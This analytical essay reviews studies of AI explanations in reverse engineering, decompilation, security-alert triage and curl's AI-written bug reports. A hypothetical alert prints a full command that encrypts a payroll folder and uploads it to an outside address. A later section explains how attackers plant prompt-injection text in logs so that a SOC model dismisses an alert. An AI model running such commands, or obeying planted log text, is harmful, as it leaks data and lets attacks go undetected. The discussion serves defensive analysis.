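The times for individual functions may explain why experts gained so little overall. Experts with and without the AI took significantly different amounts of time on six functions. Four of these implement common algorithms, such as Base64 decoding, which recovers data encoded as letters and digits. Experts with the AI spent well under half the time on these. The paper reports this speed-up as at least 248% in its results section but as up to 2.4 times in its abstract. Experts with the AI took at least three times as long on the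 other two functions, which contain custom logic. They also returned to one of these, which handles incoming requests, up to 14 times more often.

A function that implements a standard algorithm is easy to explain to an expert. "This is Base64 decoding" is enough, because the expert already knows how Base64 works and can check the claim against a few telltale constants. Custom code can't be explained so briefly. Basque and colleagues think that experts left the routine functions to the AI and spent the time they saved on the unusual ones. The times fit that explanation, but they also fit the possibility that the AI's descriptions of the custom functions misled the experts.

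### Names from the AI and names from people

Reverse engineers record what they learn by replacing labels such as `a2` with meaningful names and by adding comments and types. Without the AI, experts recovered an average of 54 such items per program and novices recovered 41. With it, the averages rose by 56% to 84 for experts and by 63% to 67 for novices, although the abstract lists the increase as at least 66%.

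The extra items did not go with better understanding. Participants who recovered more names, types and comments by hand tended to score higher, but the number that the AI wrote had no significant relation to the score. One possible reason is that the AI's names were worse. To check this, the researchers compared names for functions with the original source code and counted any name with the same meaning as correct:

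| Kind of function | Number | AI's names correct | People's names correct |
|---|---|---|---|
| Known algorithms | 13 | 85% | 66% |
| All others | 37 | 57% | 65% |

Basque and colleagues call the difference on known algorithms statistically significant, but they report p = 0.4. If the AI and the people were equally good, a gap at least this large would appear by chance 40% of the time, and the study's threshold for significance is 5%. The figure may be a misprint for 0.04. As printed, it does not support the claim, though the experts' faster work on standard algorithms points the same way. On the other functions, the difference could easily be due to chance (p = 0.82).

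The AI's names were about as accurate as people's, so poor quality alone can hardly explain why they did not help. Basque and colleagues suspect that the benefit comes from choosing the name. Before naming a function `check_password`, a person has to decide what it does, and accepting the AI's name skips that step. The Cisco programmers who annotated their own code before a review may have benefited in the same way.

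Causation could also run the other way, because people who understand a program can name more of its parts. But there is some further evidence for the idea. Basque and colleagues looked at pairs of successive actions and found three in which using the AI went with a higher understanding rate. All three ended with the participant changing something by hand. The most common by far, with 154 cases, was an AI summary followed by the participant naming the function themselves.

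An experiment on ordinary programming gives indirect support. In *The Comprehension Gap in LLM-Assisted Software Development* (2026), 35 people searched for small changes researchers had planted in code. They took about two minutes with code they had written themselves, two and a half with code they had produced with an LLM, and more than four with code they had never seen. They also found more changes in their own code, and remembering the code was an important factor. Writing code takes more effort than naming a function, so naming probably has a smaller effect.

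This complicates the design of explainers. A button that names everything in a program at once is the obvious product to build, but its user may learn little from it, even though the result looks finished.

### A flaw that was not there

Twenty of the 96 write-ups described something in the program incorrectly. Ten came from sessions with the AI and ten from sessions without it, so the AI did not make such mistakes more common. Three participants wrongly reported that RPC had a buffer overflow, an error in which a program writes more data into a block of memory than the block can hold. The AI had suggested the overflow to each of them, in three different functions, when they asked it to look for vulnerabilities. No one working without the AI invented a feature of the program in this way.

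The three spent at least 231% more time than average on those functions. A confabulated flaw takes a long time to dismiss because no single run can rule out an overflow, even though a single input can confirm a real one. The participants could not try inputs, since they were not allowed to run the program. Maintainers of open-source software face the same problem when strangers send them reports of imaginary flaws.

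Participants asked the AI to find vulnerabilities only 34 times, and those who did so more often tended to have lower scores. That may be partly because people who were already lost were more likely to ask. Still, this feature drew more scepticism than any other. One expert wrote of a suggested memory error, "It said there was a UAF, but it's not." (UAF stands for "use after free", in which a program goes on using memory that it has already given up.)

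### What the fastest participants did differently

Basque and colleagues also compared the ten participants who had the highest understanding rates when using the AI with the ten who had the lowest.

| | Highest ten | Lowest ten |
|---|---|---|
| Novices and experts | 5 and 5 | 9 and 1 |
| Points per minute | 0.17 | 0.02 |
| Requests to the AI | 29 | 37 |
| Requests per function | 1.71 | 3.43 |
| Requests about longer functions | 4.73 | 9.69 |

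The total number of requests did not differ significantly, but the fast participants rarely asked repeatedly about the same function, and they used the AI less on functions longer than the median of 31 lines. Only eleven people in the study asked all their questions about a function the first time they opened it and afterwards read the code without help, and nine of them were fast participants.

Basque and colleagues picked the two groups by their results, so these habits are not a sound basis for rules. Someone who does not understand a function will ask about it again, so repeated questions may be a result of confusion rather than its cause. An experiment could settle which it is by limiting randomly chosen participants to one question per function. The finding that LLMs perform worse on larger functions also calls for caution, because the researchers inferred it from how people used the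 AI and did not grade its answers by function length.

People who often used LLMs for reverse engineering were more careful with them, making 20 requests per program against 35 for the others, but their understanding rates were no better. The experts thought more highly of several AI features than their results justified. One of them worried that novices with an LLM "would reverse a lot of programs without actually understanding what's going on". The average novice's scores do not support this worry, but the nine novices in the bottom ten are a reason to take it seriously.

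### Newer models on the same two programs

The AI in this experiment is now old. In October 2026 Doria and colleagues gave RPC and Secrets to nine newer models that worked alone, with the same decompiler and again without running the programs. Another LLM graded the write-ups on the seven factual points, and its grades matched those of human annotators on 94.5% of a sample. On RPC, GPT-5.5 Pro, Claude Opus 4.8 and the Chinese model Kimi K3 scored between 6.6 and 6.8, while the ten best human participants averaged 6.7. On Secrets, the three models scored between 6.0 and 6.2, while the people averaged 5.5. The models took about 11 minutes per program, while the people took 75 minutes for RPC and 47 for Secrets.

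Missing names seem to trouble strong models much less than people. When Doria and colleagues gave the same three models the original source code instead of decompiler output, the models' scores barely changed, though scores on RPC were already close to 7 and had little room to improve. The models may also have seen the code before, because the programs and their source were public before some of the models finished training. Such exposure is plausible, since Benkraouda, Cai and colleagues (2026), in *Reveree*, found that models could reproduce the secret answers to some published challenges from the description alone. When the models in that study failed a challenge, they had usually recovered the program's structure but not worked out what the code was for, and more time or reasoning effort rarely helped.

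Weaker models failed in a way that would be hard for a reader to notice. In about 12 of the 17 runs that scored zero, the model made at most two requests for information about the program but still handed in a complete write-up. Such a report is almost entirely confabulated. A reader could catch this by checking the log of what the model opened, without knowing anything about the program.

The strong models also worked differently from people. They jumped around the program and seldom looked at a function twice, whereas on RPC about 86% of the top participants' function views were return visits. The best models never used the tools for renaming and commenting, so an analyst who opens the program afterward finds no new names or comments and has only the write-up to go on. Doria and colleagues did not test whether a person who reads the write-up understands the program.

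Real programs are also harder than the ones in these studies. Once decompiled, 1.9% of the Linux system programs that Doria and colleagues sampled, and 39.1% of the Windows applications, would fill or exceed a context window of one million tokens. Neither study used *obfuscated* code, which is deliberately made hard to read, as malware often is. *Can LLMs Deobfuscate Binary Code?* (2026) shows how obfuscation can turn a few lines that sort a list into a maze of numbered cases and fake branches. At the heaviest level of obfuscation in the paper's benchmark, DeepSeek-R1, a reasoning model from 2025, preserved about 63% of the program's meaning by the benchmark's own measure.

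### Cleaner code that does something else

An LLM can also rewrite decompiler output as tidy code with sensible names. In the user study for *ALT4Decompile* (2025), an AI decompiler, 12 participants compared versions of the same functions. ALT4Decompile's versions got the most votes, and the least experienced participants benefited most. One of the questions they voted on was which version best preserved the original's behaviour, but votes can't settle that the way running the code can.

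Liu, Huang and colleagues (2026), in *CODEFUSE-DEBENCH*, give a small example from two conventional decompilers, Ghidra and angr. The original function takes five whole numbers and returns the position, counting from 0, of the first one that is not greater than zero. Ghidra's version contains the expression `return (0 < e) + 4`, which takes most people a moment to work out. angr's version is a chain of conditions that is easier to follow than the source code, but it is wrong because it declares the five inputs as numbers that cannot be negative.

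A researcher compares the behaviour by compiling the recovered code and running it on the same inputs as the original. Given the numbers −3, 0, 1, 1 and 1, the original returns 0 because −3 is not greater than zero. In angr's version, the computer reads the bits that stand for −3 as 4,294,967,293, moves on to the second number and returns 1. Ghidra's version correctly returns 0. If none of the test inputs were negative, all three versions would return the same results and the error would go unnoticed.

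The same researchers compared whole programs in this way. Decompiled code often does not compile at first, so they let an LLM repair it over as many as 50 rounds. With the model GLM-4.7 repairing the output of IDA Pro, 445 of 640 test programs compiled. Of these, 15 printed exactly what the original printed, 117 matched it in part and 310 failed. The test is strict because each program contains about 30 small functions. Even if each function were right 90% of the time, all 30 would be right in about 4% of programs.

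The decompilers that produced the most readable code, as rated by LLM judges, also preserved the programs' behaviour best. But the pattern reversed when the researchers changed how they compiled the original programs. With the most aggressive optimisation for speed, the decompiled code was the least readable but matched the originals' behaviour best.

The most direct evidence on decompilers that use LLMs comes from *When LLM Decompilers Recompile More and Preserve Less* (Liu, Raff and Micinski, 2026). The researchers used a *fuzzer*, a program that generates many varied inputs, to explore the original function. They then ran the original and the recovered code on all those inputs and compared the values returned, the memory written and any crashes. A function counts as matched only if the two versions agree on every input. They could still differ on an input the fuzzer never tried, so the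 matched rates are upper limits.

One of their functions, decode6, shows how an AI rewrite can pass its tests and still be wrong. The function converts a cell's number into its column and row on a grid. The cells fill the grid in vertical strips six columns wide, and the last strip gets whatever width remains. On a grid 16 columns wide and 8 rows high, two full strips take up 12 columns and leave 4 for the last. Cell 100 lies in that last strip, at column 12 and row 6. An AI decompiler called SK2Decompile used one variable for both the normal width of 6 and the narrower width of 4. For cell 100, its code therefore treats the earlier strips as 4 columns wide and returns column 8 and row −2, which does not exist. The code passed all ten tests that came with the function because none of them used a cell in the last strip. On 100 generated inputs, its results matched the original function's 70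 times, while the results from plain Ghidra and Hex-Rays code matched every time.

The researchers applied the method to 291 functions from open-source libraries:

| Decompiler | Rewritten by | Compiles | Matches the original |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ghidra | none | 75% | 74% |
| Ghidra | LLM4Decompile | 90% | 62% |
| Ghidra | DeGPT-Qwen | 74% | 69% |
| Hex-Rays | none | 81% | 78% |
| Hex-Rays | GLM-5.2 | 80% | 71% |
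| Hex-Rays | SK2Decompile | 41% | 32% |

Every rewrite lowered the share of functions that matched the original. LLM4Decompile, a model trained for this task, made much more of the code compile. It repaired 42 functions that Ghidra had got wrong or that would not compile, but broke 77 that Ghidra had got right. When Ghidra's code compiles, it is nearly always correct, so a failure to compile is a useful warning. With LLM4Decompile, about three in ten of the functions that compile behave differently from the original, with no compile error to warn the reader.

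Worse for security work, the rewriting can hide vulnerabilities. Liu, Raff and Micinski also decompiled 287 functions with known vulnerabilities, each of which crashes on a particular input. In 25 of the 183 functions that compiled after LLM4Decompile had rewritten them, the crash no longer occurred, while plain Ghidra lost none of the crashes. An analyst who tested the rewritten code would conclude that the program was safe, although the program in use still had the flaw.

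The errors tend to come with invented details. Where a conventional decompiler cannot determine a type, it prints a placeholder such as `undefined4`, which shows the reader that the type is unknown. Most AI decompilers replace these placeholders with proper-looking names and types, some of which have no basis in the program. Among rewritten library functions that compiled, 53% of those with an invented field, type or function call behaved differently from the original, compared with 20% of the rest. This does not prove that the inventions cause the errors, because difficult functions may lead to both. But DeGPT-Qwen, which edits the decompiler's text in place and keeps most of the placeholders, lost 5 percentage points of matched behaviour, compared with 12 for LLM4Decompile, and none of the known crashes disappeared.

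*The Evolution of Binary Decompilation in the Modern Era* (2026), a literature review, finds that researchers have done little to test whether code keeps its meaning after decompilation. Until tools routinely run such tests, an analyst needs the decompiler's own output next to the model's tidied version, because the tidied version alone does not show which details came from the program and which the model made up.

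## Security alerts: what analysts ask an AI to explain

Analysts in a *security operations centre* (SOC), the team that watches an organisation's computers for attacks, usually have minutes to assess an alert, while the reverse engineers in Basque and colleagues' experiment could spend an hour on one small program. Sensors on laptops, servers and networks record activity, and detection rules raise an alert when something looks suspicious, such as an unusual command or a login from a new country. The analyst then closes the alert as harmless or passes it on as a possible attack. Many alerts are false alarms. According to SANS Institute's *AI-Human Collaboration in Modern SOCs* (2026), sponsored by the company TandemTrace, a mid-sized organisation with 4,500 alerts a day would need nearly 94 analysts working without breaks to give each one ten minutes.

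### One alert, explained

Suppose an alert arrives at 02:14 about a server that holds payroll records. A sensor has recorded this command, run from the administrator's account:

`tar czf - /srv/payroll | openssl enc -aes-256-cbc -pbkdf2 -pass file:/root/.k | curl -sk -T - https://203.0.113.25/u/0417`

The analyst pastes the command into an LLM, which might answer: "This compresses the payroll folder, encrypts it with a password stored in /root/.k, and uploads it to the server at 203.0.113.25 without checking the server's identity. Attackers often steal data this way. But the address belongs to your backup provider, so this is probably a scheduled backup."

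The first sentence is correct, and the analyst can check it against the manuals for the three programs. The last sentence is a confabulation, because nothing in the command shows who owns the address. Even a perfect explanation of the command would leave the main question open, because the analyst would still have to find out who owns the address, whether a scheduled job runs the command, whether the same upload happened on earlier nights, and who was using the administrator's account.

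An LLM can also raise false alarms. *From Chasing Ghosts to Missed Attacks* (Thurner, Jost and colleagues, 2026) draws on interviews with 25 people who work in SOCs. One manager said that an LLM kept flagging the nightly backups as suspicious, since large encrypted transfers at night look like data theft to anyone who doesn't know the company's routine.

Sometimes the command alone is enough to judge an alert, but it is hard to read. *RACONTEUR* (Deng, Li and colleagues, 2024) shows two commands that look much alike. Both open a network connection and read from it, but one checks whether a web server is working, while the other gives control of the machine to whoever is at the far end. To test how well explanations separate such cases, the researchers had GPT-3.5 use them to judge whether each command was malicious. It recognised 60% of the malicious commands from GPT-4's explanations and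 79% from those of Raconteur, a small model trained for the task. These models are old, and an LLM did the judging, so the test is weak evidence of what an analyst would have concluded.

### 3,090 questions in ten months

The best record of what analysts ask comes from eSentire, a company that monitors its customers' systems around the clock. It gave analysts access to GPT-4 through a web page. *LLMs in the SOC* (Singh, Tariq and colleagues, 2025) analyses 3,090 of the 3,122 queries that 45 volunteer analysts sent between May 2023 and March 2024. More than half of these analysts did the first sorting of alerts. GPT-4 had no access to the internet or to eSentire's systems, and company policy barred analysts from entering confidential data.

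About 31% of the queries asked about commands, typically "what does this do". Another 22% asked for help with writing, such as "make this better" for an incident description, and 11% were about code, scripts or search patterns. The rest covered many smaller topics, including malware, software tools and network traffic. Two in five queries were the only one in their conversation, and three quarters of the longer conversations had only two or three queries.

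One analyst sent roughly 600 of the queries, while 34 of the 45 analysts used the system lightly. The ranking of the most common tasks stayed the same when the researchers left out the ten heaviest users. Use grew from fewer than ten queries a day in the first summer to more than 30 in early 2024.

Analysts asked whether something was malicious in only about 4% of all queries. Among the roughly 950 queries about commands, the share was 3%, and those came from just seven people. Singh and colleagues infer that analysts want evidence and prefer to decide for themselves. They recommend that investigation tools show the evidence without giving a verdict.

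That may be right, but there are other possible reasons. GPT-4 could not see the company's records, so it would have struggled to judge whether something like the payroll upload was an attack, and the analysts presumably knew this. They also may not have needed to ask for a verdict. When GPT-4 explained a command, it often inferred the purpose, pointed out suspicious behaviour and suggested what to do next, which could come close to a verdict. Counting questions cannot show how much the analysts relied on these implied verdicts.

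The study's main limitation is that it cannot show whether the explanations were right. Singh and colleagues read GPT-4's answers for context but did not grade them, partly because the company had removed identifying details that a grader would need. They also had no data on how quickly or accurately the analysts resolved their alerts. Continued use is weak evidence of quality, since an analyst who believes a false explanation has no reason to stop asking. One analyst gave up after two wrong answers in a row, and two others carried on despite apparent errors, but there may have been other errors that left no trace.

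*It is Not Yet Another Tool* (2026) cites a study by Kramer and colleagues with 18 analysts and 50 real incidents. Summaries that an LLM wrote alone often omitted critical details or got facts wrong, but analysts who wrote them with the LLM could save effort and produce more readable text.

Experts could still grade a sample of eSentire's command explanations, because what a command does rarely depends on the customer. If they doubted an explanation, they could run the command on an isolated machine. This would give an error rate for the most common use of the tool, though only for a model from 2023.

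### Trials of speed and accuracy

Most of the measured gains come from companies testing their own products. *Randomized Controlled Trials for Microsoft Copilot for Security* (Edelman, Bono and colleagues) describes Microsoft's first large trials of its assistant, Security Copilot. Participants from outside the company summarised an incident, analysed a script, wrote a report and chose a response. Microsoft reported that people new to the job were 26% faster and 44% more accurate with it, as quoted in Windows Central's *Microsoft's Security Copilot is helping cyber responders be 73% more accurate*. Microsoft's results for experienced analysts were smaller, at 22% faster and 7% more accurate, according to Futurum Group's *Microsoft Copilot for Security Increases the Efficacy of Security*. As with the reverse engineers, the less experienced seem to have gained more.

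The Cloud Security Alliance (2025), an industry association, randomly assigned 148 participants to investigate two alerts with or without an AI product from Dropzone AI. It reported that those using the AI were 45 to 61% faster and 22 to 29% more accurate. Dropzone is a member of the association and supported the project, but the association says the company had no influence on the content. The accuracy claim is hard to reconcile with the scores in Virtualization Review's *Cloud Security Alliance AI Report Goes 'Beyond the Hype'* (2025). It gives 97% with the AI and 86% without it for one alert, and 85% and 81% for the other, which are improvements of only 13% and 5%.

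The closest to an independent trial is a smaller study from CSIRO, Australia's national science agency. In *Bridging Expertise Gaps*, Tariq, Singh and colleagues (2025) had 34 people judge emails and 24 look for network intrusions. When working with an LLM, participants raised fewer false alarms about emails and missed fewer intrusions, and they kept some of the benefit when they later worked alone. The researchers present this as help for non-experts, so the results may not carry over to a working SOC.

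The most informative trial is again from Microsoft. In *Randomized Controlled Trials for Phishing Triage Agent*, Bono (2025) tested an AI agent that sorts emails employees have reported as possible *phishing*, messages that try to trick people into giving up passwords or money. Microsoft (2026) has advertised such trials as independent, although Bono works for the company. In the trial, 167 professional security analysts from outside Microsoft each judged 25 emails.

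The headline result is that analysts with the agent found 6.5 times as many attacks per minute. This assumes that they skip every email the agent calls harmless, as users of the product do, and 83% of the gain comes from skipping. It also assumes an agent that makes no mistakes. With a less accurate agent and more attacks among the emails, the factor falls to 3.1. When analysts had to read all 25 emails, those with the agent took about 50 minutes and those without it about 57, a difference that could be due to chance. (The paper labels these times as seconds per email, but they only add up as minutes for the whole set.)

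The agent had classified all the test emails correctly, so Bono had to create errors to study. To make a false all-clear, Bono labeled a real attack harmless and attached a plausible justification, avoiding any detail that obviously clashed with the email. To make a false alarm, Bono labeled a harmless email an attack and justified it the same way.

| The email was | The agent called it | Wrong answers with the agent | Wrong answers without it |
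|---|---|---|---|
| an attack | an attack | 12% | 18% |
| an attack | harmless | 46% | 17% |
| harmless | harmless | 14% | 35% |
| harmless | an attack | 54% | 48% |

A false all-clear from the AI agent nearly tripled the share of analysts who missed the attack. A false alarm had no clear effect, perhaps because analysts spent longer on the emails they thought were malicious. The analysts had reason to trust the agent, since they had been told that 95% of its all-clears were correct.

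Judging by the table, having people review the all-clears could catch many of the attacks the agent misses. If the agent wrongly clears 20 attacks out of 100, analysts who see its verdict would catch about 11 of them, and analysts who don't see it about 17. Without review, all 20 would be missed. Each participant saw only one false all-clear, so the exact rates are uncertain, but the gap is too large to be due to chance. Bono nevertheless concludes that review has little benefit because people mostly agree with the agent. A better policy might be to have analysts read a random sample of the cleared emails with the verdict hidden.

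Other researchers have let an LLM close alerts of all kinds. In the test runs of *Dynamic Reasoning in Next-Gen Detection and Response* (2026), the LLM closed about 90% of the false alarms, which would save analysts a lot of work. But it also closed between 21 and 31 of the 59 alerts where it was given evidence of an attack. A more careful system did much better in *From Investigation Failures to Reliable SOC Agents* (2026). It had GPT-4.1 investigate each alert by a set procedure, at about 11 cents per alert. Of 1,247 alerts, it left 18.4% for further investigation and dismissed the rest. Of those it dismissed, 99.3% were harmless, but about seven were attacks. The head of security at one large company told Thurner and colleagues that the company had gone from chasing false alarms to missing attacks.

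### When an attacker writes the evidence

Some of the text that an AI has to explain in a SOC may be deliberately misleading, unlike the outdated comments in old COBOL and assembly code. Attackers choose the names of their files, the usernames they try and the wording of their emails, and sensors copy much of this into the logs. *Poisoning the Watchtower* (2026) points out that an LLM reading those logs receives the evidence and the analyst's instructions both as plain text. Text that an attacker plants so that the model will treat it as an instruction is called *prompt injection*. To plant it, the attacker only has to do something that the sensors record, and does not need access to the model.

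Planted text can also mislead without giving any instruction. The thief in the payroll example could name the upload to suggest a routine backup, and the explainer might repeat this as fact, as GPT-4 did with the false comments about basketball. A misleading file name can fool a person too, but a person is unlikely to follow instructions written in one. Phishing emails are especially awkward because the attacker writes nearly all of the text, and Microsoft's agent closes the ones it judges harmless without showing them to an analyst.

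Without being asked, many of the people Thurner and colleagues interviewed brought up attacks that use planted text to mislead an AI, and one said that no reliable defence exists yet. Running the model on the company's own machines keeps confidential data inside the company but doesn't stop planted text from reaching the model. Interviewees who test defences by attacking them worried most about AI tools with broad permissions. One had found a badly configured Copilot that revealed every employee's salary. A misled AI does less damage if it can only write descriptions than if it can also unlock accounts or open files.

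Most interviewees wanted a person to check the output before it takes effect. Some suggested having a second LLM check the first. This should catch some ordinary errors, but if both models read the same log, text planted in it may mislead both. Many also wanted the AI to give reasons and sources. Others doubted that this would help, because the sources are sometimes wrong and an LLM can give convincing reasons for a false conclusion, as with Bono's borrowed justifications.

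A majority thought that an LLM should err on the side of raising alarms and leave the final check to people. This makes particular sense as a defense against planted text, since an attacker usually wants the alert closed. If the explainer can raise an alert's priority but cannot close it, the attacker has less to gain from misleading it. The drawback is that analysts still have to deal with most of their false alarms, which many SOCs want the AI to reduce.

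Whatever the AI says, the analyst's safest evidence is a record that the attacker could not have written. This rules out the server's own list of scheduled jobs, an obvious place to check the payroll alert, because someone who controls the administrator's account can add the upload there and it will look like any other backup. The analyst should look for an approval in a system that this account cannot change, or call the person who runs the backups.

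## Bug reports to the curl project: explanations of flaws, false and true

Unlike security analysts, who choose which alerts to ask an AI about, maintainers of open-source software (software whose source code anyone may read and use) receive AI-written explanations they never asked for. Strangers send them reports of *vulnerabilities*, which are bugs that an attacker could exploit, and someone has to check whether each report is true. The fullest record of this work comes from Daniel Stenberg, the founder and lead developer of curl, who has blogged for years about the reports his project receives.

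curl transfers data over the internet. It can fetch a web page, upload a file or collect email, and other programs use its library, libcurl, to do the same. Few people run it knowingly, but it is in phones, cars, televisions and printers. Stenberg (2026), in *The pressure*, puts the number of installations at perhaps thirty billion. The code runs to almost 180,000 lines and has about 50,000 more words than *War and Peace*, according to Stenberg's *A new breed of analyzers* (2025). In 2025 a security team of seven judged the reports, and Stenberg was the only one of them who worked on curl full-time.

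### What a report has to explain

A vulnerability report should identify the faulty code, the conditions under which it fails and what an attacker could do as a result. Stenberg's guide *Do excellent vulnerability reports* (2026) also asks for the affected versions, a proposed fix and a *reproducer*, a script or small program that the team can run to see the fault happen. Reporters should begin with a few sentences in their own words. Stenberg calls this a reality check, because someone who can't write them doesn't understand the flaw well enough. The check is easy to cheat on, since an LLM can write those sentences too.

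Someone on the team usually replies to a report within an hour, as Stenberg explains in *From suspicion to published curl CVE* (2025). Several members then study the claim, and if it seems to have merit, they question the reporter and run any code that came with the report. This takes a few hours to several days, and most reports turn out not to describe a security problem.

### Convincing reports of flaws that did not exist

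In April 2019 curl started a *bug bounty*, a programme that pays people who report real vulnerabilities. By January 2024 it had received 415 reports, of which 64 described real vulnerabilities and 77 mostly described ordinary bugs, according to Stenberg's *The I in LLM stands for intelligence*. The other two thirds were neither, but the team had usually dismissed them quickly. Stenberg complained that LLMs were changing this by making worthless reports look competent, and that the better a report looked, the longer the team took to reject it.

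In May 2025 Stenberg began asking everyone who submitted a bug report whether they had used AI, and banning those who sent what he calls AI slop. Willison (2025), a software developer who blogs about AI, quotes him as writing that curl had still not seen "a single valid security report done with AI help".

*Death by a thousand slops* (Stenberg, 2025) reported that slop made up about 20% of the year's submissions by July. Stenberg suspected that AI had also written some of the other bad reports. Only about 5% of all submissions described genuine vulnerabilities. That percentage is rough because, at two reports a week, it represents about three vulnerabilities in half a year.

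Each report occupied three or four people for between 30 minutes and three hours each, or 1.5 to 12 hours of work in total. Genuine vulnerabilities made up 5% of reports, so the team handled 19 other reports for each one. Some of those 19 described ordinary bugs worth fixing, but together they took at least 28 hours of work. Some of Stenberg's colleagues might have had only three hours a week for curl.

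### A false report and a true one

On 28 December 2023 a user sent curl a report titled *Buffer Overflow Vulnerability in WebSocket Handling*. (WebSocket lets two programs keep a connection open and exchange messages.) The reporter pointed to a line that copies a short piece of random text into a block of memory with the standard function `strcpy`. If the text were longer than the block, it would cause a buffer overflow, which might let an attacker run their own code.

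Most of this is true. The line exists, `strcpy` does not check whether the text fits, and careless use of it has caused many real vulnerabilities. The reporter proposed a common fix, and an overflow could have the effect described.

The report's false claim is that the text could be too long. curl generates the text from 16 random bytes, which always become 24 characters, and the block has room for 40. Just before copying, the code checks the length and stops if the text would not fit. The mistake was easy to miss because it appeared among the steps for reproducing the flaw. One step was to provide text longer than the block, which nobody can do because curl does not accept this text from outside.

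Stenberg could not tell at a glance that the report was false. It was in proper English, from a user with a decent reputation, and it looked better than the average first report. Nineteen minutes after acknowledging it, he had read the code three times without finding the overflow it described. He asked the reporter where and how the overflow would happen, got a series of hallucinated answers, and closed the report that afternoon. He thought an LLM had probably written the answers but could not be sure.

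On 11 August 2025, curl received the first report in which AI seemed to have found a real vulnerability. It came from Google's Big Sleep team, which uses an AI agent to search for unknown flaws, and concerned cookies, the small pieces of data that websites store on a visitor's computer. According to curl's public notice, *CVE-2025-9086* (2025), the flaw can occur when a site sets a protected cookie over an encrypted connection, curl then contacts the same site without encryption, and the site tries to replace the cookie. curl should ignore the attempt, but a faulty comparison reads beyond the end of a block of memory, which either crashes the program or may let the site replace the cookie.

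Both accounts name a specific mistake in memory handling, and a reader could not tell from the style which one is true. But the first depends on a condition that can't occur, while a maintainer can create every condition in the second and watch what curl does. The comparison slightly favors Big Sleep, because the curl team published the notice after working on the flaw, and the original report may have been less clear.

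### The lists that led to real fixes

In September 2025 a security researcher, Joshua Rogers, sent curl a list of more than 200 possible problems, found mostly with an AI code analyser called ZeroPath. The list led to about 50 fixes. The rest were false alarms, points on which the team disagreed, and issues too minor to fix. Rogers then sent two more lists, with 47 and 158 entries, and Stanislav Fort of the security company Aisle reported about twenty possible problems. Stenberg was impressed by the quality of these reports, and the rate of obvious false alarms stayed low.

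Most of the findings were small, such as mixed-up variables or memory that the program never released. Conventional analysers had missed them partly because they can only examine versions of curl that someone has built, and curl has too many possible versions to build them all. The AI tools read the source code directly, including parts that hardly any other analyser had checked.

The tools also relied on the programmers' comments. In one case, a comment described a function's argument as optional, and the tool correctly reported that curl would crash if a caller left it out. The argument was required, so the team corrected the comment rather than the code. Stenberg warned that outdated comments could also cause the tool to report flaws that don't exist, much as false comments misled LLMs about old assembly code.

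Slop kept arriving during the same months, so the results evidently depended on the tool and on how people used it. ZeroPath, which sells the analyser, promotes it as a way for engineers to spend more time on difficult problems. In Stenberg's view, the people who had sent slop often meant well too, but had believed AI companies' marketing.

### More reports, and better ones

curl ended the bounty on 31 January 2026, as Stenberg announced in *The end of the curl bug-bounty* (2026). He hoped that this would remove some of the incentive to send nonsense. Rogers thought it was a great idea, according to etn.se's *cURL removes bug bounties*.

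By April, curl was receiving reports at about twice the rate of 2025, and nearly all involved AI. But Stenberg (2026) wrote in *High-Quality Chaos* that slop was no longer a problem and that 15 to 16% of reports described real vulnerabilities, about the same share as before LLMs.

Better tools are probably the main cause of the trend, though the end of the bounty may have put off some of the worst reporters. When someone asked what curl had changed, Stenberg, under the username bagder, replied, "we changed nothing, the tooling changed". People from more than two dozen other projects, including Firefox and the Linux kernel, told him that they saw the same trend, and those projects are unlikely to have all ended bounties in the same month.

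In May, Anthropic's model Mythos found only one vulnerability, a minor one, in its first scan of curl. The finding was correct but gave little indication of how many flaws remained. The next release, in June, fixed 18 vulnerabilities, a record for curl. The company Aisle found six of them, as it reported in *AISLE Discovers 6 CVEs in curl* (2026).

By 17 November 2026, the team had confirmed 81 vulnerabilities that year, Stenberg wrote in *Actual curl rewrites in rust* (2026). The bounty had taken more than six years, from April 2019 to July 2025, to produce the same number. Most of the new ones are less serious, but fixing them has made the software safer.

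The work wore the maintainers down, so they refused all vulnerability reports in July 2026 to recover. Stenberg called this possibly the project's best decision in a long while. In October, about ten reports a day came in over one weekend and the days that followed, according to Stenberg's weekly email of 24 October 2026. The team then decided to handle all but the most serious vulnerabilities in public so that outsiders could help judge them. This gives attackers a little longer to exploit the minor ones.

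### What a reproducer proves

A maintainer who gets a report without a reproducer has to rule out the flaw by reading the code, as Stenberg did with WebSocket and as the reverse engineers did when their AI suggested overflows that did not exist. If the reporter supplies a reproducer, the maintainer can run it on their own copy of curl and see whether the fault occurs. This checks the claim independently and makes the reporter do the work of proving it. The team needs such a test anyway to confirm that its fix works.

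Luna Tong, a researcher at Anthropic, used an AI scanner to find the first curl vulnerability since 2023 that the project rated high severity. Tong reported it on 15 September 2026 with a complete software environment for reproducing it, and the team confirmed it within hours. But the reproducer could not show how likely an attack was on other machines. Stenberg judged that an attempt would most likely just crash the program.

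Stenberg wrote in *ignore the slop* (2026) that reproducers used to be one of the hardest parts of a report to produce, but now take "just a prompt or two". Asking for one therefore no longer deters careless reporters by demanding effort. A reproducer still works as evidence, because an honest test won't reproduce a flaw that doesn't exist, however easy the test was to write.

A description of a test is much weaker evidence than the test itself. In *High volume AI vulnerability reports* (2026), a set of slides, Stenberg debunks a report that included the output of a debugging session and a crash. The session was made up, the crash does not happen, and the function blamed for it does not exist.

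A test that runs may still test the wrong thing. In October 2025 someone who acknowledged using AI sent curl another report about the same `strcpy` call in the WebSocket code. The reporter quoted the length check that makes the copy safe but still called the copy vulnerable. The report included a working test, a small server that reported triggering the vulnerability as soon as a program connected and sent its random text. Every WebSocket program sends such a text, so the server would have reported the same result for a program with no flaws. Maintainers can catch this by running the test on a program they know is safe, much as researchers can test a method for explaining neural networks on a random network.

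Some real flaws are also very hard to trigger. One of the bugs from Rogers's lists had been in the code for more than a decade, in a place that tests seldom reach. Rogers also found a real mistake in a feature that did not work for other reasons, so no test could have reached it. The team removed that feature. If the curl team had refused to read reports without a reproducer, it might have lost many of the autumn's fixes. A more sensible rule is to look first at reports that have one, and to accept others from people whose earlier findings were sound.

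### True reports also take time to judge

A reproducer shows that something happens, but a person still has to decide whether it matters. On 5 November 2026 curl received 45 claimed vulnerabilities from OSS Scanner, a service with which Anthropic checks important open-source projects. The findings came with reproducers, and many also had proposed fixes. Stenberg (2026), in *curl on OSS-Scanner*, reports the team's verdicts:

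| Verdict | Findings | Share |
|---|---|---|
| Real vulnerability | 5 | 11% |
| Ordinary bug | 36 | 80% |
| Not a bug | 3 | 7% |
| Completely wrong | 1 | 2% |

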